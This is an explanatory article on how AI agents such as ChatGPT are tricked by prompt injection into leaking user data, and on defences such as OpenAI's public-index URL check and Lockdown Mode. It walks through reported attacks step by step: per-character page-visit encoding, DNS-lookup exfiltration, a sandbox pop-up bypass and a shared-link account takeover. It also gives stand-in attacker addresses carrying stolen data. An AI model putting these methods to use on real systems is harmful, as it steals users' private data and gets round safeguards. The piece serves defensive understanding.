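The post is clear that the rule covers images as well as pages. Its examples of requests that a user may never notice are loading an embedded image and previewing a link. It doesn't explain how the check handles other files that a page may request after it has loaded. In Chen and colleagues' tests, OpenAI's fetching software didn't run a page's scripts or download a separate script file that the page referenced. A page therefore can't use scripts to trigger more requests, at least in this software. A full browser such as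 Atlas, where OpenAI also applies Safe Url to navigation, does run scripts.

OpenAI also objects that users visit more than a few famous sites, so a strict list would produce frequent false alarms and people would learn to click through them.

Lists work when an agent has only a few places to send data. *The Framing Gap* reports experiments in which an allowlist of destinations stopped every leak, however the attacker encoded the data. But the test agent had only one trusted destination, and the paper notes that the method's drawback is that it blocks legitimate traffic. A company might accept that for an agent that uses three internal systems, but an allowlist would make little sense for a product that people use to search the web.

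The public-index check also causes false alarms, for new pages and for sites that refuse OpenAI's crawler. OpenAI can spare users some of these by having the agent look for another source instead of showing a warning. OpenAI's January and March posts don't give the size of the index or the share of requests that end in a warning, so it's hard to judge how much better the check works than a good list of trusted sites.

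### Four addresses

The table applies the rule to four invented addresses.

| Address | In the crawler's records? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `https://news.example/2026/river-flood` | Yes | The agent can open it automatically |
| `https://news.example/2026/river-flood?ref=22-Elm-Road` | No | The agent tries another site, or the user sees a warning |
| `https://council.example/notices/road-closed-today`, published an hour ago | Not yet | The agent tries another site, or the user sees a warning |
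| `https://school.example/open-day-draft`, typed by the user | No | The agent opens it, as Rehberger understands the rule |

A list of trusted sites would treat both news addresses alike because they belong to the same newspaper, whereas requiring an exact match separates them. Exact matching would also reject a harmless addition such as `?ref=newsletter`, unless the crawler had found that version of the link.

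The council's notice is safe, but the check treats its address like one containing stolen data. A page that went up an hour ago and an address that the agent has just invented are both missing from the crawler's records. A user who needs the notice can open it from the warning. Once the crawler has found the page, the agent can open it without asking.

The evidence for an exception for addresses that users type themselves is less direct. OpenAI's January post doesn't mention one. Rehberger described it on Embrace The Red as his understanding of ChatGPT. As he describes it, the exception covers the typed address, not the whole site, so a version with Ruth's street added would still need to pass the lookup.

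A press report of 8 January, *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026), supports him. According to the report, OpenAI responded to ZombieAgent by restricting links from emails, so that ChatGPT would open one only if it appeared in a well-known public index or the user had provided it directly in a prompt.

The tests by Chen and colleagues also fit. A researcher entered questions by hand into the ChatGPT app, along with the addresses of newly created test pages, and ChatGPT opened the pages. A crawler had probably not recorded them yet. But the study was about how AI products download and store pages, and it doesn't discuss warnings.

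Such an exception is reasonable because Ruth has decided to contact the site if she types the address herself, and the model has had no chance to add anything from her email to the address.

### What OpenAI promises

OpenAI says the safeguards aim at "one specific guarantee", that the agent fetches pages and images without "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself".

The promise doesn't extend to data the agent sends by email, or to a link that the user opens after seeing the warning.

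OpenAI then names four things that the check does not automatically guarantee:

- that the content of a web page is trustworthy
- that a site won't try to manipulate the user through social engineering
- that a page won't contain misleading or harmful instructions
- that browsing is safe in every possible sense

The check has these limits because a match shows only that the crawler has seen an address, not that anyone has judged the page. The site's owner, or a stranger posting a review, can add hostile instructions after the crawler's visit, and the agent can still open the page automatically because the address hasn't changed.

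## What can still leak when only public addresses are opened automatically?

An agent that opens only addresses a crawler has already recorded can still send a message by choosing which ones to open, as Johann Rehberger pointed out on Embrace The Red when he assessed the public-index check in 2026. The attacker gives each public page a meaning, and the agent spells out the secret by visiting the pages in turn.

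ZombieAgent worked this way using addresses from an email, which the new check would block. But Rehberger points out that the owner of a larger website or blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, enough for the letters a to z and the digits 0 to 9. The attacker could also assign meanings to thousands of pages. Every request would pass the lookup, since the agent opens each address exactly as the crawler recorded it. Anthropic's Claude has a similar rule about exact addresses, and Willison (2026) reported in July that Ayush Paul had found a loophole in it.

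### How much a choice of page can carry

A bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. Choosing between two pages carries one bit, choosing among four carries two, and choosing among *N* carries log₂(*N*). In their 2008 paper *Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP*, Borders and Prakash used this rule to measure how much spyware or a disloyal employee could smuggle out through web requests. They calculated the most information the requests could contain rather than searching them for secrets, because encryption makes a secret unrecognisable. In one test, half an hour of reading blogs produced 191 requests totalling 108,565 bytes. Almost all of that was predictable from earlier traffic, leaving at most 351 bytes of new information.

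Rehberger gives no such figures for ChatGPT. The ones below are a new calculation that applies the 2008 rule to his example, and they assume an agent that never makes a mistake. If the agent makes *n* visits, each to any of *N* pages, the most it can send is

*n* × log₂(*N*) bits.

With 36 pages, an attacker can leak one letter or digit per visit, or 5.17 bits. Leaking two characters per visit requires 1,296 pages, one for each possible pair, and leaking three requires 46,656.

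Stealing long text this way is slow. An email of 2,000 letters and digits would take 2,000 visits with 36 pages, one for each character, or 1,000 visits with 1,296 pages, one for each pair of characters. In ShadowLeak, by contrast, a single request carried an employee's name and home address.

Short secrets are much easier to leak. Sending a seven-digit code all at once would take ten million public addresses, but sending it one digit at a time takes only 70, ten for each position, and seven visits. A burglar who only wants to know which week Ruth's house will be empty needs 52 addresses and one visit.

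### Would Rehberger's remedies stop it?

Rehberger proposes that ChatGPT either keep a copy of each page for a few minutes, so that a second request never reaches the attacker, or refuse to open the same address twice in a session. Both measures would make it harder to send the same character twice, but he had not checked whether ChatGPT already uses either of them.

The table gives the limits for 36 pages and ten visits. ChatGPT would open ten addresses per prompt when Schwartzman tested it in 2024.

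| What the attacker can use | Calculation | Most that ten visits can send |
|---|---|---|
| Repeat visits, in a known order | 10 × log₂(36) | 51.7 bits |
| No repeats, in a known order | log₂(36 × 35 × … × 27) | 49.7 bits |
| No repeats, order lost | log₂(36 × 35 × … × 27 ÷ 10!) | 27.9 bits |

Banning repeats reduces what the attacker can learn by only two bits. Losing the order of the requests reduces it far more, but neither remedy changes the order in which they arrive. Requests do sometimes arrive out of order, which Rehberger counts as an obstacle for attackers. Even then, the attacker can learn 27.9 bits, more than the 23.3 needed for a seven-digit code.

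To reach these limits, the model would need a more complicated code than one page per letter. ZombieAgent's method is simpler and uses a separate page for each character in each position. For ten characters, that takes 360 public pages and restores the full 51.7 bits, without repeat visits or any need to know the order of the visits. Against this method, Rehberger's remedies mainly raise the number of pages an attacker needs from 36 to 360, and a large blog may have that many.

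Over a longer session, banning repeat visits limits leaks more than temporarily storing copies of pages, because the copies expire and the attacker can then use the pages again. Under the ban, each page works only once, so an agent that visits all 36 in a chosen order can send at most 138 bits, or about 27 characters.

Limiting the number of images in each answer, as Rehberger suggested in 2023, would reduce *n* directly. With one image per answer and 36 pages, the attacker gets one character per answer, however the pages are arranged. The limit would also have to cover page visits to work against an agent that browses.

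### What makes the attack difficult

The attacker still has to get the model to follow hostile instructions despite its training, and the model then has to look up each character correctly. Listing thousands of pages makes the instructions long and conspicuous, unless the addresses follow an obvious pattern. The attacker also has to put the pages on a site whose logs they can read, early enough for OpenAI's crawler to find them.

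Those logs may be hard to interpret, because the attacker can't tell from a visit by OpenAI's servers which user the agent is working for. If two victims' agents visit at the same time, the attacker could mix up their letters. ChatGPT may also not contact the site if it reuses a copy downloaded for another user, as Chen and colleagues saw it do. The attacker can't force a fresh download by adding a parameter to the address, because the changed address would no longer match the index.

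OpenAI could also notice a long run of visits to one site by monitoring its own records, as Rehberger suggested for url_safe in 2023.

He calls the 2026 safeguard "a significant improvement" but not a complete fix. Attacks have become more complex, he writes, while leaking a few bits still seems straightforward. The arithmetic supports his assessment, because the check protects long secrets better than short ones, and some of the most damaging secrets, such as login codes, are short.

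### When the agent's ordinary choices give the user away

Rehberger's attack needs an agent that follows a stranger's instructions to encode a secret. An agent can also reveal something about its user just by opening the pages most relevant to the task. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) presents an attack called SNOOP that exploits this.

In SNOOP, the attacker places a link to further references on a page the agent is likely to read. The link leads to the attacker's site, which offers pages on different subjects. Suppose a user asks why flu can be more dangerous than COVID-19 for children. The agent first picks "Biological Mechanisms" over "Clinical Outcomes", then "Immune Response" over "Pathogenesis". Each choice appears in the attacker's log and narrows down the question, although the agent never sends the user's words.

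Liang and colleagues tested four agents, including OpenAI's Codex, each with three language models, on a stored copy of part of the web. When the site offered four clearly different pages, the attacker could infer what the agent was looking for in 93.8 percent of the trials that produced a signal. With 16 pages, accuracy fell to 50 percent. A choice among 16 pages can in theory reveal four bits, twice as much as a choice among four. But if the errors were spread evenly across the other options, the 16-way choice revealed only about 1.0 bit, compared with 1.6 for the four-way choice. SNOOP therefore uses a series of narrow questions. It needed an average of 6.5 of these questions per user query when tested on 500 queries from StackExchange, a group of question-and-answer sites.

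For the queries that left a readable trail, SNOOP recovered the main concepts with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 means the attacker found everything and added nothing false. In a separate test with longer conversations, it recovered facts about users, such as their interests and where they lived, with a score of 0.80. The researchers also planted instructions that told the agents to send a secret outright, but only 0.38 percent of those attempts delivered the complete secret.

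SNOOP recovers subjects and interests, not passwords, so the comparison is more even than it appears. An agent has no reason to choose a page based on its user's password unless someone tells it to.

The researchers did not test SNOOP against a public-index check. SNOOP creates new pages as it runs, and a check like OpenAI's would treat a newly invented address as unverified. But the check covers only addresses, so an attacker could publish a few dozen plain ones, wait for the crawler to record them, and then change the text on the pages to suit each visitor. The rule itself does not prevent this, but nobody has shown that it works against ChatGPT.

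Liang and colleagues propose hiding which pages the agent chooses. Their software downloads everything a page links to, whatever the user's task, and the agent then picks from the stored copies. The attacker's log therefore shows visits to all the pages, and SNOOP's score on the StackExchange questions fell from 0.89 to 0.39. The attacker still saw nearly all the true concepts, but mixed with many false ones. The defence required 4.3 times as many page downloads. The same idea would weaken Rehberger's attack, since an agent that always loads all 36 pages doesn't spell out data through its choice of pages.

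### Private links in public collections

Ramadan and colleagues found in their February 2026 study, *The Silent Spill*, that a public collection of addresses can contain private links. Their sources did not include OpenAI's index.

The researchers started with the six million addresses they had collected between January and April 2025. They discarded files such as fonts and stylesheets, then looked for telling words such as "token" or "invoice" and for unusually long or complex addresses. That left 832,714 addresses, of which 149,450 still led to a working page that anyone could open. Their software loaded each of these pages in a browser, read the text, including text inside images, and flagged the 12,331 possible leaks.

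Login credentials and similar tokens made up 43.3 percent of the flagged cases, and financial details 19.6 percent. Seven pages displayed complete backup codes, which let a person into an account without the usual second login step. The researchers checked only 12 to 34 cases in each category by hand, so the share of false alarms is uncertain. They estimate that at least 3,954 of the 5,343 cases flagged in the login category were real. They could not measure how many leaks the software missed.

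Exposed links can also stay open for a long time. When the researchers revisited 2,000 of the flagged addresses after 75 days, 38 percent still opened without a login.

OpenAI's January post doesn't mention any filter to keep links to private documents out of its index. If the index included one, an agent could open it without a warning and bring a stranger's contract or invoice into the chat, though anyone who found the link could open the document without an agent.

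Opening a link can also have side effects, such as using up a password-reset code. Ramadan and colleagues opened 24 kinds of reset and backup-code links on their own accounts. This neither cancelled old codes nor created new ones, so automatic visits to those links seem harmless.

### Users who approve the warning

When an address isn't in the index, the user may get to decide whether to open it. The best recent figure on how often people click through warnings comes from a different kind of prompt, the permission requests that Anthropic's programming agent, Claude Code, used to show before running many commands. Users approved 97 percent of them, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

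Most of the requests were probably harmless, so that rate alone doesn't prove carelessness. Anthropic also paid 1,053 professional testers to work on coding tasks, and once per session replaced a permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 percent of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more requests.

The testers worked in a practice environment where they had nothing of their own to lose, and Anthropic published the results to explain why it was replacing most of these requests with an automated check. Link warnings are also rarer than permission requests in a coding session. OpenAI says Safe Url rarely intervenes, which should reduce fatigue. But about five in six testers approved the dangerous command even early on, so rarity alone is unlikely to make people read carefully.

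Reading each warning carefully may not be enough either. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) argues that approving actions one at a time can't reveal their combined effect. If an attacker's letter pages are not in the index, a user might approve an address ending in `/e`, then one ending in `/l`, and see nothing private in either.

### Products that don't run the check

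A check protects only the products that use it. Rehberger calls this the "final real-world risk", because some of OpenAI's own developers may not know the safeguard exists. He had seen the same problem with the url_safe check, which took about nine months to reach the iPhone app. In 2023 he suggested running such checks on OpenAI's servers, so every app would get them at once.

By March 2026, OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* listed page visits in the Atlas browser and Deep Research among the places where Safe Url applies. Researchers kept finding the old image leak elsewhere.

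PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes a leak through the page where developers read the logs of apps they have built on OpenAI's models. The security company used a mock tool for checking bank customers' identities. Hidden instructions in material from the web made the model produce an image address containing a customer's personal data. The tool's own filter blocked the answer, but when a developer opened the log to see what had gone wrong, the log page displayed the image, and the data went to the attacker. Several of OpenAI's tools for testing new apps had the same fault.

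PromptArmor reported the flaw on 17 November 2025, and the report was closed as not applicable on 4 December. OpenAI hadn't seen the report because Bugcrowd had handled it. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI reopened the report on 22 January 2026 and indicated that a fix was under way. OpenAI published its post about safe links six days later.

Codex had a similar problem that spring. PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* describes a user who asks Codex to sort through some emails, one of which contains hidden instructions. Codex then writes an image whose address points to a Google form prefilled with the text of other emails. Loading the image submits the form, and the attacker reads the emails in its responses. An exact lookup would have rejected that address. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April 2026, and OpenAI has fixed it.

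The security company Rapid7 lists an image leak in the Codex app for Mac as CVE-2026-14898. It may be the same flaw or a separate one. The entry reports no known use by attackers, and its description doesn't mention a fix.

OpenAI responds to gaps like these by saying the link check is one of several defenses, alongside training models to resist prompt injection, product controls, monitoring and continued testing by its own red team. In PromptArmor's Codex demonstration, none of the other defenses stopped the emails from leaking.

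## What else does OpenAI do to stop data leaving, and has it held?

In addition to safety training and Safe Url, OpenAI has offered Lockdown Mode since February 2026. This optional ChatGPT setting turns off or limits features that can send data to outside servers. These protections have not stopped every leak. In 2026 two security companies, Check Point and Parameter, published four ways to get private data out of ChatGPT, one of which worked with Lockdown Mode on. Safe Url did not stop them because none sent the data out through the agent's own page visits. OpenAI has fixed all four.

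### An automated attacker for Atlas

On 22 December 2025, two months after launching the Atlas browser, OpenAI reported that it had built an automated attacker to search for prompt injections that work on Atlas's agent. The attacker is a language model that OpenAI trained by reinforcement learning, in which a model receives a reward when it succeeds and gradually does more of what earned the reward.

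The attacker model can draft an injection and send it to a simulator, which predicts how the Atlas agent would respond and returns a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions. The attacker model uses that record to revise the draft, and can repeat the process several times before settling on a final version. The record is far more informative than a pass or fail result. It also gives OpenAI an advantage over criminals, because the company doesn't show outsiders the agent's full reasoning.

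OpenAI chose reinforcement learning partly because the harms it worries about take many steps. An agent that sends someone's money to a stranger has to work through a series of pages first, and it isn't clear until the end whether the attack succeeded. Most earlier automated testing had found simpler failures, such as an agent writing a particular phrase or misusing a tool once. According to OpenAI, the new attacker could steer an agent through harmful tasks of tens or even hundreds of steps. It also found strategies that had not appeared in the company's human testing or in outside reports.

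In the published example, the attacker plants an email in a user's inbox with instructions to send the chief executive a resignation letter. The user later asks the agent to draft an out-of-office reply. The agent finds the email while doing this, takes the instructions as genuine and resigns on the user's behalf instead of writing the reply.

A link check would not have prevented this, because the harm came from the email the agent sent. OpenAI tells users to read the confirmation requests that its agents should show before sending an email or completing a purchase. In its description of the resignation, OpenAI doesn't say whether the agent showed one.

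OpenAI trained a new version of the agent against the attacks it had found, concentrating on those that still worked, and released it to all Atlas users. It also used the records to look for improvements outside the model, for example in monitoring. The post gives no success rates from before or after the update, so it's hard to tell how much the training helped.

OpenAI wrote that prompt injection, like scams aimed at people, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and that the nature of the problem makes firm guarantees difficult. In *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*, Nolan (2025) reported for Fortune a more basic objection from Charlie Eriksen, a researcher at Aikido Security, who said that this kind of testing can catch obvious failures without changing the underlying problem. Until there are much clearer limits on what agents may do and whose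 instructions they should follow, Eriksen thinks ordinary users have reason to doubt that the benefits are worth the risk.

OpenAI advises people to use Atlas logged out of their accounts when a task doesn't need them. It also recommends narrow requests. Telling an agent to read the inbox and do whatever is necessary makes it easier for a malicious email to influence what the agent does.

### Planning for an agent that has been fooled

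In its March 2026 post on agent design, OpenAI assumes that some attacks will succeed. It argues that the most effective injections now resemble social engineering, in which a con artist uses a plausible story to get people to do something. Companies already have ways to protect staff from this, and OpenAI wants to apply similar protections to agents.

The post's example is a customer support worker who can give out refunds and gift cards. Some customers will lie, perhaps claiming that a refund never arrived, and others will make threats. The employer gives the worker rules but expects some lies to work, so ordinary software caps the refunds and flags likely phishing emails. A convincing liar may still get a refund, but the cap limits the company's loss.

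Many security companies recommend a different defence, often called an AI firewall, which scans everything before it reaches the agent to detect malicious text. OpenAI says these systems don't usually catch fully developed attacks, because recognising one amounts to recognising a lie, often without the necessary context.

The staff-restructuring email in OpenAI's example, which worked half the time, shows the difficulty. It referred to a meeting the previous Thursday and placed its request for an employee's details among routine office tasks. A filter given only the email can't determine whether the meeting took place or whether the compliance system it mentions exists. The user had also asked the agent to check every source that might have information about a new-employee process, and the attacker's email appeared to be one.

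This email closely matches the one in ShadowLeak, down to the user's request, so OpenAI was probably describing an early version of that attack.

OpenAI uses source-sink analysis to decide where to put limits. Engineers list a product's sources and sinks, then look for paths from a source to a sink. In the restructuring attack, the source was the inbox and the sink was the agent's ability to open a web page. OpenAI can't block the inbox because the user wants the agent to read email, so it puts a check on opening web pages.

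For the same reason, OpenAI also applies Safe Url outside the chat window. In Atlas, the check covers bookmarks as well as page visits, presumably because an agent could save an address containing private data for the user to open later. In Deep Research, it also covers searches, since search queries, like addresses, can carry private text. Small programs that ChatGPT builds in Canvas, its workspace for writing and code, run in a sandbox, a restricted environment that detects unexpected attempts to contact other computers and asks the user for permission. Apps that run inside ChatGPT have similar protections.

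This method protects only the sinks that engineers have identified. Web requests are an obvious sink, but Check Point and Parameter found leaks through features that hardly anyone would think of as a way to send a message, including an on-screen keyboard for mathematics.

### Lockdown Mode

Safe Url still lets an agent contact the outside world after passing a check, while Lockdown Mode removes many of those connections. OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode on 13 February 2026 for its Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans, and began extending it to personal accounts and self-serve business accounts on 4 June. According to The Hacker News, a security news site, it is available on all personal plans, including the free one.

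OpenAI's announcement, *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), describes the restrictions as deterministic. The software switches a feature off, so the result doesn't depend on whether the model recognises an attack. The help page *Lockdown Mode* lists these changes:

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | ChatGPT reads only stored copies of pages, and search results may be missing or out of date |
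| Images | ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web; users can still upload and generate images |
| Deep Research | Off |
| Agent mode | Off |
| Canvas | Users can't give the code it generates access to the network |
| File downloads | ChatGPT can't download files to analyse, but can work on files the user uploads |
| Apps on personal and self-serve business accounts | ChatGPT blocks live access to outside services, and changes made through apps, where these conflict with the protections |

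Browsing stored copies prevents leaks because no request reaches the website. If the agent in the earlier example tried to open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=22-Elm-Road-empty-from-14-March`, OpenAI's software would look for a stored copy, find none and stop, so the attacker's server would have nothing to log.

Lockdown Mode should also stop the attack that Safe Url doesn't block, in which an agent spells out a secret by visiting public pages in a chosen order. The agent would read OpenAI's stored copies of those pages, so the pages' owner couldn't see which ones it had picked.

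This setting makes ChatGPT less useful. Ruth could still ask it to compare removal firms, but it might use last month's prices. She would probably have to type in her moving date too, because ChatGPT would no longer have live access to her email. Anyone who pays for ChatGPT mainly to use Deep Research or agent mode would lose those features. OpenAI says most people don't need the setting and suggests it for people such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations.

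Personal users can also turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat. This makes the setting more convenient, but users are most likely to do it when a task needs live web access or a connected service, which is when the protection would matter most.

### What Lockdown Mode leaves open

Lockdown Mode doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent. A company that turns on Lockdown Mode for its staff therefore has to restrict Codex separately.

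In employer-managed workspaces, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically turn off every app, because some staff can't work without them. Administrators choose which apps people can use and what each app may do. OpenAI advises them to consider who could see the result of each action. For example, if an agent can comment on a document that an outside supplier can open, a comment containing a confidential price would reach the supplier without the agent opening any web address. OpenAI rates such an action as high risk, even in an app the company trusts, unless the administrator can confirm that no attacker could see the result.

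OpenAI considers reading from a trusted app less dangerous because reading changes nothing that an outsider could notice. But the app can still supply confidential data that another feature then leaks. Administrators therefore have to consider the apps in combination, and OpenAI warns that unforeseen combinations may still pose a risk.

Prompt injections can also still reach the model through a stored page or an uploaded file, so an attacker who can't get data out may still be able to change the answer. For example, the hidden text that made an agent recommend the wrong flat could work just as well from a stored copy of the listing. Lockdown Mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory either, so if an attacker has already planted a false fact there, as Radware did with a user's medical history, it could still affect later answers.

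OpenAI's help page says plainly that the setting does not guarantee that data can't leak.

### Elevated Risk labels

OpenAI introduced a standard "Elevated Risk" label on the same day as Lockdown Mode. It marks a few features in ChatGPT, Atlas and Codex whose network access creates risks that, according to OpenAI, the industry's protections don't yet fully address.

One example is the screen where a developer gives Codex internet access. The developer can limit Codex to an allowlist of sites and choose which kinds of request it may send. The label appears beside these controls, with an explanation of what the access changes, what could go wrong and when it makes sense to allow it.

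The label helps people decide whether to turn a feature on, but it doesn't block an attack once one is under way. OpenAI plans to remove the label from a feature when it decides that the safeguards are good enough for general use, but the announcement gives no criteria for that decision.

### A leak through name lookups

When ChatGPT analyses data, it runs code in a container, an isolated environment that OpenAI creates for the job. OpenAI had blocked ordinary internet connections from these containers. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) shows how data could still leave through the domain name system (DNS), which computers use to look up the IP address for a site's name.

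Suppose code in the container looks up this invented name:

`22-elm-road.attacker.example`

The query passes through a chain of DNS servers until it reaches the one responsible for `attacker.example`. The attacker runs that server and can read Ruth's street in the query. This works without anyone opening a web page, or a site with that name even existing. Longer data has to be sent in several pieces, which the attacker puts back together. The replies can carry data to the container, and the researchers used them to send commands and run them there.

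An attacker could start the leak by getting the victim to paste a prepared prompt into a chat, after which every new message in that chat could leak. Check Point suggests that an attacker could advertise the prompt as a trick for unlocking paid features, since people would then expect it to look strange. The attacker could also put the instructions in a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that anyone can set up for others to use. The victim then only had to open it and start chatting.

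The researchers built a custom GPT that acted as a personal doctor. A user uploaded laboratory results and described symptoms, and the patient's name and the GPT's medical assessment went to the researchers' server. When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT said it had not.

The model's training offered no protection because the model treated the container as unable to send data out, so it didn't identify the lookups as a transfer it should refuse or ask the user about. Safe Url didn't help either, because looking up a name doesn't involve requesting a page.

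OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem itself. It finished deploying the fix on 20 February 2026, a week after launching Lockdown Mode. Check Point's report doesn't mention whether the leak worked during that week with Lockdown Mode on.

### A shared noticeboard between accounts

Check Point found another way to get data out of the containers, this time to another ChatGPT account. Check Point Research published the finding on 8 September 2026 in a report by Alexey Bukhteyev.

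Code often needs extra software packages. OpenAI supplied them through an internal service rather than give the containers internet access to download them. Different users' containers couldn't contact each other, but they could all reach this service and attach text or data to the items stored there. A container could read what another account's container had attached.

TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* describes how the researchers used it. The attacker posted instructions on the noticeboard. When the victim next asked ChatGPT something, ChatGPT read the instructions, retrieved messages from the victim's connected Gmail account and posted them on the noticeboard. The attacker then collected them from a separate ChatGPT account. If the data was too long for one notice, the code split it across several.

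The victim first had to introduce the text that told ChatGPT to look at the noticeboard. According to Divya (2026), in *ChatGPT Flaw Could Let Attackers Steal Gmail Data Across User Accounts*, this text could be in a shared conversation, a prompt the victim pasted or the settings of a custom GPT. After that, an ordinary question was enough to trigger the attack, and the answer on the screen looked normal.

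Restrictions on outside connections couldn't stop this attack, because the data reached the attacker without leaving OpenAI's systems. Lockdown Mode would probably have protected a personal user's Gmail messages by cutting off live access to Gmail. But OpenAI doesn't list running code among the features Lockdown Mode disables, so it may not have protected what the user had typed into the chat.

TechRadar reported that OpenAI closed this route. Check Point warned that other companies' AI products may have similar shared services. It calls an assistant in this position a "coerced insider", a system that an attacker has tricked into using access its owner gave it for good reasons.

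### A pop-up window that got past Lockdown Mode

Check Point's next finding directly tested Lockdown Mode. The weak point was Preview, a ChatGPT feature that turns HTML, the code behind web pages, into a working page inside the chat. Because the HTML could contain anything, ChatGPT displays the page in a sandbox, where it can't read the app's stored data and shouldn't be able to contact other computers without the user's consent.

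A page might try to get round this by opening a new window. ChatGPT intercepted direct attempts, but the underlying browser settings still allowed pop-up windows to open outside the sandbox, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026). Check Point's page created another frame inside itself. The new frame had its own copy of the command for opening windows, which ChatGPT hadn't modified. A window opened with that command wasn't bound by the sandbox's restrictions and could pass on the conversation.

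In the ChatGPT desktop app, this was a zero-click attack. *ChatGPTs ekstra sikkerhed er usikker* (Allan, 2026), an article on a Danish technology site, reports that the researchers used a custom GPT with malicious instructions and that the user neither clicked a link nor approved a transfer. A prepared prompt or a shared chat could also deliver the attack.

The attacker controlled everything in the new window, so the window could also show a fake ChatGPT update under the real ChatGPT icon. To infect the computer with malware this way, the attacker would still need the user to click.

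Press accounts differ on how much data was at risk. The headline of TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* refers to the user's "entire chat history", whereas Allan describes a leak of information from the conversation. Allan's narrower description fits the mechanism better, because the page in the sandbox couldn't read the app's data itself and so could presumably send only what ChatGPT had written into it.

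OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026, about seven weeks before the details became public. The bypass also shows the limits of a "deterministic" protection. Lockdown Mode didn't depend on the model's judgement, so the attack didn't need to defeat that judgement. It succeeded because ChatGPT blocked one copy of a command instead of removing the browser permission, which would have blocked every copy.

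### An account takeover through a shared chat

On 18 October, a month after that fix, Parameter reported a different flaw involving Preview. It let an attacker take over a ChatGPT account by sending its owner a link.

The link led to a real shared conversation on ChatGPT's own site, as Goyal (2026), in *Do the Math*, explains. The conversation contained an interactive graph and an HTML preview, and the attack needed both:

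1. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded MathLive, a mathematics library, into its main page. MathLive began listening for messages about its on-screen keyboard.
2. The preview, still inside its sandbox, sent MathLive a message containing a new keyboard layout. Browsers allow sandboxed pages to send such messages, and leave it to the receiving page to check who sent them.
3. MathLive didn't check. It accepted the layout, which contained the attacker's HTML, and added it to the main ChatGPT page.
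4. The HTML created a new frame that the browser treated as part of ChatGPT's site. ChatGPT's rules blocked most scripts there but allowed those from YouTube, and the researchers found a way to make YouTube return a script containing their own code.

That code had the same access as the signed-in user. In tests between separate accounts, it listed the victim's recent conversations, opened a private one and sent part of it to the researchers' server. It could also have taken other actions in the victim's account. Parameter reported no use of the flaw outside its own tests, according to The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026).

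In the most reliable version, the victim opened the link and clicked the Preview button once. The researchers later got the preview to open by itself, so opening the link was enough. They repeated this three times in a separate account, and their code ran after about 4.5 seconds.

An early version of the attack would have been much less useful to a criminal, because the victim first had to connect an app that the researchers controlled. The researchers then put the HTML in an attachment, but the graph disappeared when they shared the conversation, so MathLive never loaded. The attack became practical only when they found a way to keep both the HTML and the graph in one public link.

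In this attack, the attacker prepared the conversation in advance and the victim's browser ran the code. The victim's AI agent wasn't deceived, so training a model to resist prompt injection couldn't have prevented it. According to Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, the code could send the stolen data out in the address of an image, the same method Samoilenko used in 2023. Safe Url couldn't stop this, because the attacker's code could request the image directly.

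OpenAI raised the report's severity from P2 to P1, its most serious category, and by 26 October ChatGPT's web app was rejecting the messages the attack used. The Hacker News pointed out that blocking YouTube scripts alone would not have been enough, since a preview could still have added HTML to the main page. The fix took eight days, much less time than the fixes for ShadowLeak or ZombieAgent. OpenAI paid a $5,000 reward, which Willison considered "a bit cheap" for such a serious flaw.

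## How do other companies' AI products handle the same risk?

Any product that opens web pages for its users needs a rule about who may supply the addresses. OpenAI relies on an independent crawler, apparently with an exception for addresses the user types. Anthropic accepts addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, but not ones that its model, Claude, composed. Microsoft's Copilot limits which sites its images can come from. Researchers have got data past Anthropic's and Microsoft's restrictions. They have also found that data can leak through messaging apps without the agent requesting the page.

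### Anthropic: addresses already in the conversation

In September 2025 Anthropic added a web fetch tool to its API, which developers use to build products on Claude. According to the documentation page *Web fetch tool*, Claude is not allowed to "dynamically construct URLs". It can open only URLs that have appeared in a user's message, in the output of a tool the developer runs, or in the results of an earlier search or fetch.

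If Ruth's agent used this tool, the hostile review could still cause Claude to write a URL containing her street and moving date. The tool would not open the URL, because it would appear only in Claude's output.

This rule doesn't need an index, so it handles new pages better than OpenAI's check does. For example, a council notice posted an hour ago opens normally if the user pastes in the link. But strangers can also put text into a conversation, as Willison (2025) pointed out in *Claude API* when the tool launched. Developers often paste outside material, such as an email, into the same message as the user's question. The tool then treats every address in the email as if the user had supplied it, and would accept a list with one address per character, like ZombieAgent's.

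Willison still thought the ban on addresses composed by the model gave good protection, because the common attacks depend on the model building an address that contains the stolen data. The consumer Claude app had the same restriction when he tried it.

Anthropic has since added a length limit to the rule. *網頁擷取工具*, a newer, Chinese-language edition of its documentation, limits addresses to 250 characters. That prevents anyone from sending a whole email in one request, but shorter secrets still fit. The address that carried Ruth's street and moving date in the earlier example has 69 characters.

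The tool also refuses an address that appears to contain a password or an access key, unless that credential is in the user's message or the developer's instructions. Unlike the ban on composed addresses, this check works only if the tool recognises the credential, so an attacker might get round it by encoding the credential first.

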